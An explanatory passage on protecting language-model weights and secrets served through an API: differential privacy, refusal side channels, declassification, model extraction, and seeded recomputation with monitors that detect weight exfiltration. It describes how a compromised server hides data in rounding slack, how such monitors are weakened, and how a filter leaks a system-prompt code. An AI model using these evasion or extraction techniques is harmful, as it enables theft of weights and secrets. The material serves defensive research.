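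A model's owner can avoid this problem by making the training procedure differentially private. One way is to limit how much each training record can change the weights at each step and then add noise to the change. The privacy guarantee then covers the weights and anything the server computes from them without going back to the training data, so customers can send any number of prompts without weakening it.

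This guarantee protects individual training records, such as one patient's letter. If a secret appears in m records, the guarantee for it weakens from ε to mε. It doesn't cover text that the server later adds to the model's context. It doesn't keep the weights secret either, and it would still hold if the owner published them.

### Why the weights can't be the private record

Suppose the owner treats all the weights together as the one record to protect. The API would then have to satisfy, for any two sets of weights w and w′, every prompt u and every possible answer y,

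Pr[M(w, u) = y] ≤ e^ε × Pr[M(w′, u) = y].

One possible w′ has a final layer of all zeros, so it gives every token in a vocabulary of 100,000 the same probability, 0.001%. If ε is 1, the real model can't give any token a probability above 0.0027%, whatever the prompt, so its text would be nearly random.

For the real model to give the right token a probability of 90%, ε would have to be at least ln(90,000), or about 11.4, for that token alone. A procedure that is ε-differentially private in this sense has a min-entropy leakage of at most 1.44ε bits, which is about 16.5 bits here. The counting bound already limits each token to 16.6 bits, so by this measure the privacy guarantee gives the owner almost no extra protection.

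The owner could instead protect each weight separately, by comparing only sets of weights that differ in one number. A model protected this way might remain useful, because changing one weight in a trillion often has little effect on an answer. But customers could still learn what the weights do together, which is what a competitor wants to copy.

### When a refusal is an answer

Database operators can also refuse dangerous questions. Shmatikov's *Query Auditing* describes an auditor that checks whether the answer to each new question, combined with the answers to all earlier ones, would reveal something forbidden. Offline auditing looks for such breaches after the answers have been released. Online auditing has to decide whether to release each answer beforehand, and that decision can itself reveal protected information.

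Suppose an auditor refuses a question whenever the true answer would reveal somebody's exact salary. An analyst asks for the highest salary among Ann, Ben and Cal, and learns that it is $90,000. The analyst then asks for the highest salary among Ann and Ben. If it is also $90,000, the auditor can answer, because either of them might earn it. If it is lower, the answer would reveal that Cal earns $90,000, so the auditor refuses, and the analyst can infer Cal's salary from the refusal.

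Kenthapadi, Mishra and Nissim address this with simulatable auditing in *Denials leak information* (2014). The auditor may use the questions and the earlier answers to decide whether to refuse, but not the true answer to the new question. The analyst could therefore work out the decision alone, so a refusal reveals nothing new. In the salary example, the auditor would refuse the second question whether or not Cal earned $90,000, because some possible salaries would make the answer revealing. However, the auditor also refuses questions whose true answers would have been harmless.

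*Dynamic Enforcement of Knowledge-based Security Policies using Probabilistic Abstract Interpretation* (Mardziel, Magill and colleagues, 2013) describes a related method that connects auditing with declassification. The server keeps a model of what the querier believes about the secret and uses it to decide whether to answer. This is more realistic for small secrets such as a birthday than for a language model's weights, where the server would have to represent beliefs about billions of numbers and update them after every answer.

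The same leak can occur at an API. Suppose the system prompt contains a four-digit access code, and a filter withholds any answer that contains the code. An attacker asks the model to repeat "0417". The filter withholds the answer only if the code is 0417, so the attacker learns whether the guess was right. The attacker needs far fewer requests if each one asks the model to repeat a list of half the codes that are still possible. If the server allows answers that long and the model repeats the lists correctly, 14 requests are enough. The filter causes this leak, since the model might never have revealed the code by itself.

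What a refusal reveals depends on the information behind it:

| The server refuses because of | What the refusal can reveal |
|---|---|
| the prompt and a published rule | nothing about the secrets |
| the prompt and a secret classifier | how the classifier works |
| the model's answer and a published rule | something about the answer, but no more than the answer itself would have |
| the model's answer and the system prompt | the system prompt, even if the answer alone would not |

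A refusal that the model writes itself counts as an ordinary answer and uses up tokens like any other.

Simulatable auditing corresponds to the first row. To protect the access code this way, the server could refuse every prompt that asks for a four-digit number, but it is difficult to recognise all such prompts. A more practical filter could remove every four-digit number from the answers, whether or not it is the code, though this would also remove the years from a history lesson. This filter belongs in the third row, because a customer could remove the same numbers from the unfiltered answer.

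The same principle applies to the leakage limit. If the server stops after 1,000 answers, a customer can predict the cut-off by counting, so it reveals nothing about the weights. If the owner instead stops customers only once their answers have revealed too much about the weights, the time of the cut-off depends on the weights, and an attacker could learn from it.

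## Releasing no more than an honest server would

A leakage bound counts a megabyte of ordinary answers the same as a megabyte copied from the weights file. An owner who sells answers accepts the first kind of leak and wants to rule out the second. One way to do this is to compare the real server with an honest server, an ideal one that returns only the specified model output M(w, u) for each prompt u. The real server passes if an attacker can learn nothing from it that they couldn't learn from the honest one.

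Cryptographers make such comparisons precise with a simulator, an imaginary attacker who can query only the honest server. For every attacker A there must be a simulator S such that, whatever the weights are,

A's output after querying the real server ≈ S's output after querying the honest server.

Both have realistic computing power, and S may send no more prompts than A. The symbol ≈ means that no realistic test could tell the two outputs apart.

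Under this condition, attackers can choose the prompt but not the function the server computes. This rules out the "open sesame" backdoor, which robustness with endorsements allows. The honest server treats "open sesame" like any other prompt, so a simulator that sends it doesn't get the weights file.

| What the real server does | Passes? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| adds scores that the specification leaves out | no | The honest server doesn't return them. |
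| mixes in text from another customer's contract | no | The honest server answers this customer without that contract. |
| alters its answers to carry parts of w | no | The honest server's answers follow the model's probabilities and nothing else. |
| recites the system prompt because the model does | yes | The recitation is the specified output. |
| answers millions of prompts from someone training a copy | yes | The simulator can send the same prompts. |

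Whether a server is honest depends on its specification. In 2024, OpenAI's API offered log-probabilities and logit bias as documented options, so a server that supported them was honest even though they exposed the final layer. If the specification had allowed only text, returning log-probabilities would have violated it. The owner therefore has to write down every option and source of context that M may use.

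### Naming what a program may release

Delimited release, from Sabelfeld and Myers, is an older condition of this kind for single programs. The programmer marks certain expressions with `declassify`. Whenever two starting states have the same public values and give every marked expression the same value, the program must produce the same public results from both.

The public results can then depend only on the public inputs and the marked values. Someone who knew these could, in principle, work out everything else the program publishes, much as a simulator does. How the program publishes the information doesn't matter, so Sabelfeld and Sands's example `if true then p := h * h else p := declassify(h * h)` passes although the marked expression never runs.

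The definition evaluates the marked expressions in the starting state, which lets it catch laundering. Suppose a program may release the average of two salaries, h1 and h2, but first copies h1 into h2:

`h2 := h1; avg := declassify((h1 + h2) / 2)`

The permitted average is 2.5 whether the salaries start as 2 and 3 or as 3 and 2. But the program publishes 2 in one case and 3 in the other, so it fails.

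The honest-server condition is stricter than delimited release in two respects. Delimited release puts no limit on computation, so it accepts a program that releases a password's hash and then the password. The honest-server condition rejects this program because a simulator with realistic computing power can't reverse the hash. Delimited release also treats every marked expression as released. If a customer may buy either h1 or h2, the program may reveal both, and Sabelfeld and Myers say that expressing "either but not both" would need an extension. Counting prompts avoids this problem because a simulator that may send only one prompt gets only one secret.

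### The electronic wallet

The attack on the electronic wallet is another case of laundering. In the wallet program, h is the secret balance, k is the price of an item and l is the amount spent so far:

`if declassify(h >= k) then (h := h - k; l := l + k)`

The attack runs this line in a loop, halving the price each time. Suppose the wallet can hold up to $15 and contains $11:

| Price | Balance before | Enough money? | Spent so far |
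|---|---|---|---|
| 8 | 11 | yes | 8 |
| 4 | 3 | no | 8 |
| 2 | 3 | yes | 10 |
| 1 | 1 | yes | 11 |

The answers yes, no, yes, yes are the binary digits of 11, which is 1011.

Delimited release rejects the loop. If k starts at 8, balances of 11 and 12 give the marked expression the same value, since both are at least 8. But the loop ends by publishing 11 in one case and 12 in the other.

The type system blocks the attack by forbidding a program from changing a variable and later using it in a declassified expression. In a loop, "later" includes the next iteration. The attack breaks this rule twice because it changes both `h` and `k` between comparisons. A single purchase passes because it compares before it subtracts. The rule also rejects some harmless programs, such as `h := parity(h); p := declassify(h)`, which reveals less than the original value of `h`.

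However, the rule applies to each run of a program separately. If the wallet starts a new run of the purchase program for each sale, every run satisfies the rule, but someone who sets the prices to 8, 4, 2 and 1 in four sales still learns the balance.

An API has the same gap, since each request is a separate run and passes the rule. If the server instead runs as one endless loop, each new prompt it reads changes u, so the rule rejects the server even if its answers are harmless. The owner could mark M(w, u) for every possible prompt u, but the server could then release everything the honest server could ever output.

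Under Banerjee and colleagues' knowledge-based policy, an observer may learn no more at each declassification than they would from being told the current value of the permitted expression, given what they already knew from earlier releases. The policy accounts for what accumulates across releases but doesn't limit the total.

### When honest answers reveal everything

Suppose the secret is a linear model with d weights. It multiplies each number in the customer's input x by a weight and adds the results:

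M(w, x) = w₁x₁ + w₂x₂ + … + w_d x_d

A customer who knows x and the exact answer has one equation in d unknowns. With d questions, none of them a combination of the others, the customer can solve for every weight. Here is an example with three weights:

| Question x | Exact answer | What it means |
|---|---|---|
| 1, 1, 0 | 1 | w₁ + w₂ = 1 |
| 0, 1, 1 | 4 | w₂ + w₃ = 4 |
| 1, 0, 1 | 7 | w₁ + w₃ = 7 |

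Adding the three equations and halving gives w₁ + w₂ + w₃ = 6. Subtracting each equation from this total gives the weights 2, −1 and 5. The server returned only the specified output, so it satisfies the honest-server condition perfectly, even though it has revealed the whole model.

The definition of virtual black-box security has the same weakness. *On the (Im)possibility of Obfuscating Programs* (Barak, Goldreich and colleagues, 2010) studies obfuscators, which rewrite a program so that it computes the same function but is unintelligible. An obfuscated program is a virtual black box if a simulator that can only run the original program on chosen inputs could compute anything an attacker can efficiently compute from the obfuscated program's text. An owner with such an obfuscator could give customers the whole program and reveal no more than an API would. The paper proves that no obfuscator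 can achieve this for every program.

For a linear model with d weights, though, the owner can meet this standard without hiding anything. If the owner publishes the weights in plain text, the simulator can ask d questions, solve for the weights and write out the same text. Publishing the weights therefore reveals "no more than query access", because query access is enough to recover them.

The honest-server condition limits the simulator to as many prompts as the attacker uses, because otherwise a server that sent all d weights in reply to the first question would pass. A server still passes if it publishes the weights after the customer has asked d suitable questions, since the customer could have calculated them by then.

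How much query access reveals depends on the function. If a function returns 1 for a single secret 64-bit password and 0 for everything else, almost every query returns 0 and eliminates only one candidate, so it is a strong guarantee to reveal no more than query access would.

A language model lies between these examples. Customers who receive enough scores can recover its linear final layer but not the earlier layers. Honest text answers are enough to distill the model.

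### Recomputing the answers

The owner also needs to check that the real server behaves like the honest one. Rinberg, Karvonen and colleagues (2025), in *Verifying LLM Inference to Detect Model Weight Exfiltration*, propose recomputing the real server's answers on a separate machine. They assume that an attacker fully controls the inference server, which holds the weights and generates text, and that an outside partner receives its answers. In this attack, the answers look normal but carry parts of the weights file.

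The check has three steps:

1. A trusted gateway records every prompt, every answer and the seed that determines the random numbers for sampling.
2. A trusted verification server picks some of these records at random and runs the prompt and answer through its own copy of the model.
3. At each position, it uses the seed to calculate which token an honest server would have chosen and compares this with the token that the customer received.

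Without the seed, the verifier could check only whether each token was plausible, so a compromised server could choose among the plausible ones. Fixing the seed should leave exactly one correct token at each position. The seed has to come from a trusted source, because a server that picked its own seeds could use them to influence its answers and still pass the check.

The verifier processes the recorded answer in a single pass that gives the probabilities at every position. This is typically 3 to 10 times as fast as generating text. If the verifier generated the answer again, one different token would change the context for all later ones, and the two texts would diverge.

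The verifier doesn't have to check every answer. If 1% of answers carry hidden data, a random sample of 460 has a 99% chance of including at least one of them. The sample must be unpredictable, because an attacker who knew which answers the verifier would skip could hide data only in those.

### Why honest servers fail an exact match

Two honest servers with the same seed sometimes choose different tokens. Computers round the result of each addition, so the order of additions can change the total. With three significant digits, (100 + 0.4) + 0.4 gives 100, because each step rounds back down, while 100 + (0.4 + 0.4) gives 101. Graphics processors (GPUs) add long lists of numbers in an order that can depend on how many requests they are handling at once. The differences are tiny, but they can change which token a server chooses when two are almost tied.

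Rinberg and colleagues sent GPT-4o mini the same prompt 1,000 times with the same seed. They arranged the answers in a tree that branched wherever two answers diverged, and about 5% of the points in the tree had more than one continuation. When they ran the open model Llama-3.1-8B on their own server, the figure was 0.2%.

The verifier therefore has to accept any token that could result from rounding. If it would accept n tokens at some position, the server can hide at most log₂(n) bits there, which is zero when only one token is acceptable. This is the counting bound applied to the tokens that pass the check instead of the whole vocabulary.

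Rinberg and colleagues measured this limit on four open models, using 500 prompts and answers of up to 500 tokens. For Qwen3-30B, a server could secretly send less than 0.5% of what it could send unchecked, and the verifier wrongly flagged fewer than 0.01% of honest tokens. Stealing the weights would take over 200 times as long, so a theft that took two days without the check would take more than a year.

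The reduction is less reassuring for a very large service. In *Fingerprinting All AI Cluster I/O Without Mutually Trusted Processors*, Cankaya, Kryś and colleagues (2026) put the remaining capacity at about 0.1 bits per token and calculate that a cluster of 200,000 GPUs, each producing 2,000 tokens per second, could still send out a terabyte in under three days. This is a worst case in which the cluster runs at full capacity and the attacker controls every answer.

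Customers' choice of prompts also affects the slowdown, because some prompts leave the model with more plausible tokens than others. *Adversarial Entropy Inflation Against Gumbel-Based Inference Verification* (2026) reports that chosen prompts can reduce the slowdown from 200 times to about 100.

### Fewer false alarms

Even a false-alarm rate of 0.01% per token would produce about five false alarms in 250 answers of 200 tokens each, or 50,000 tokens in total. Rinberg and colleagues let each provider decide how to combine suspicious tokens into an alarm.

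*Anytime-valid detection of LLM weight exfiltration* (Ortega-Fernandez, Kowalczyk and Warr, 2026) reports that between 41% and 87% of honest answers in its tests contained at least one mismatched token, so a single mismatch is weak evidence that a server is dishonest. Its method gives more weight to mismatches where the correct token scored well above the next-best one, since rounding rarely causes those.

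Their monitor works like a gambler who starts with $1 and repeatedly bets that the next answer will contain a suspicious mismatch. The odds are set using a trusted server's answers so that the gambler can't expect to profit from honest traffic. On such traffic, the gambler has at most a 1 in 200 chance of reaching $200, however long they play. The monitor raises an alarm at $200, so its chance of ever giving a false alarm is at most 0.5%. Allowing another 0.5% for errors in estimating the odds brings the limit to 1%.

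They compared this with a simpler monitor that applies the three-way classification from Rinberg and colleagues and raises an alarm at the first token it labels dangerous. The simpler monitor gave a false alarm in at least 98% of series of 250 honest answers, while theirs gave none. Theirs also detected every attack by a server that didn't know the seed, usually within 6 to 14 answers. The simpler monitor detected none of these attacks.

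A server that knows the seed can make its changes look more like rounding differences. For each model, the table shows the highest rate of hidden data that Ortega-Fernandez and colleagues tested with an attacker that knows the seed.

| Model | Honest tokens that mismatch | Hidden bits per token | Attacks detected within 250 answers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama-3.2-3B | 0.40% | 0.036 | 100% |
| Qwen3-32B | 0.55% | 0.047 | 100% |
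| Qwen3-30B-A3B | 1.65% | 0.030 | 0% |
| OLMoE-1B-7B | 1.75% | 0.046 | 1.7% |

The monitor did badly on the two models for which an honest server produced the most mismatches. At 0.03 bits per token, leaking a terabyte would take more than 500 billion answers of 500 tokens each, but leaking a 64-bit password would take only about five.

The limit on false alarms also assumes that future prompts resemble those used to set the odds. Ortega-Fernandez and colleagues warn that the monitor may need recalibrating if the mix of prompts changes or if someone chooses prompts in response to earlier answers, as customers of a public API can.

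### Removing the rounding differences

The verifier wouldn't need any tolerance if it could reproduce the server's rounding exactly. In *Bit-Exact AI Inference Verification Without Performance Tradeoffs*, Cankaya (2026) got identical results, down to the last bit, from repeated runs of the same model by fixing the type of GPU, the software, the number format of the weights, the way the model was divided among GPUs and the number of requests processed together. The exceptions were a few models whose software added numbers in whatever order they arrived.

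Most of these conditions stay the same while a server runs. The number of requests processed together changes, but the server can record it as one whole number per step. The owner would need a trustworthy record of this number, since a compromised server that could report any value would regain some of the slack. Other researchers have instead rewritten the software so that this number doesn't affect the result. One version reduced the server's throughput by about 20%, although DeepSeek reports minimal overhead for its own.

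Cankaya also wrote a program that reproduces the rounding of four types of Nvidia GPU on an ordinary processor. In one test on part of Qwen3-4B, all 71 million intermediate numbers matched the GPU's. He estimates that checking 3,200 sequences a day for a model that uses 100 billion parameters per token would take about three server processors, or at least 30 with the extra work of imitating a GPU. If 0.1% of the records were false, a day's checks would have a 96% chance of detecting at least one.

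The program doesn't yet cover mixture-of-experts models, which use only some of their parameters for each token. Most of the largest current models are of this type. Cankaya designed the method for verifying agreements between rival states and didn't test it against weight theft. But if only one token were acceptable at every position, a server with a trusted seed couldn't hide information in its choice of tokens without risking detection.

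Even exact recomputation checks only that the server's output matches that of the model it is supposed to run. If poisoned training data has taught the model to reveal its system prompt after a trigger, the verifier's copy will produce the same answer, and the verifier will approve it. The verifier will also approve every honest answer that a competitor collects for distillation. Rinberg and colleagues say distillation requires "an entirely different set of defenses".
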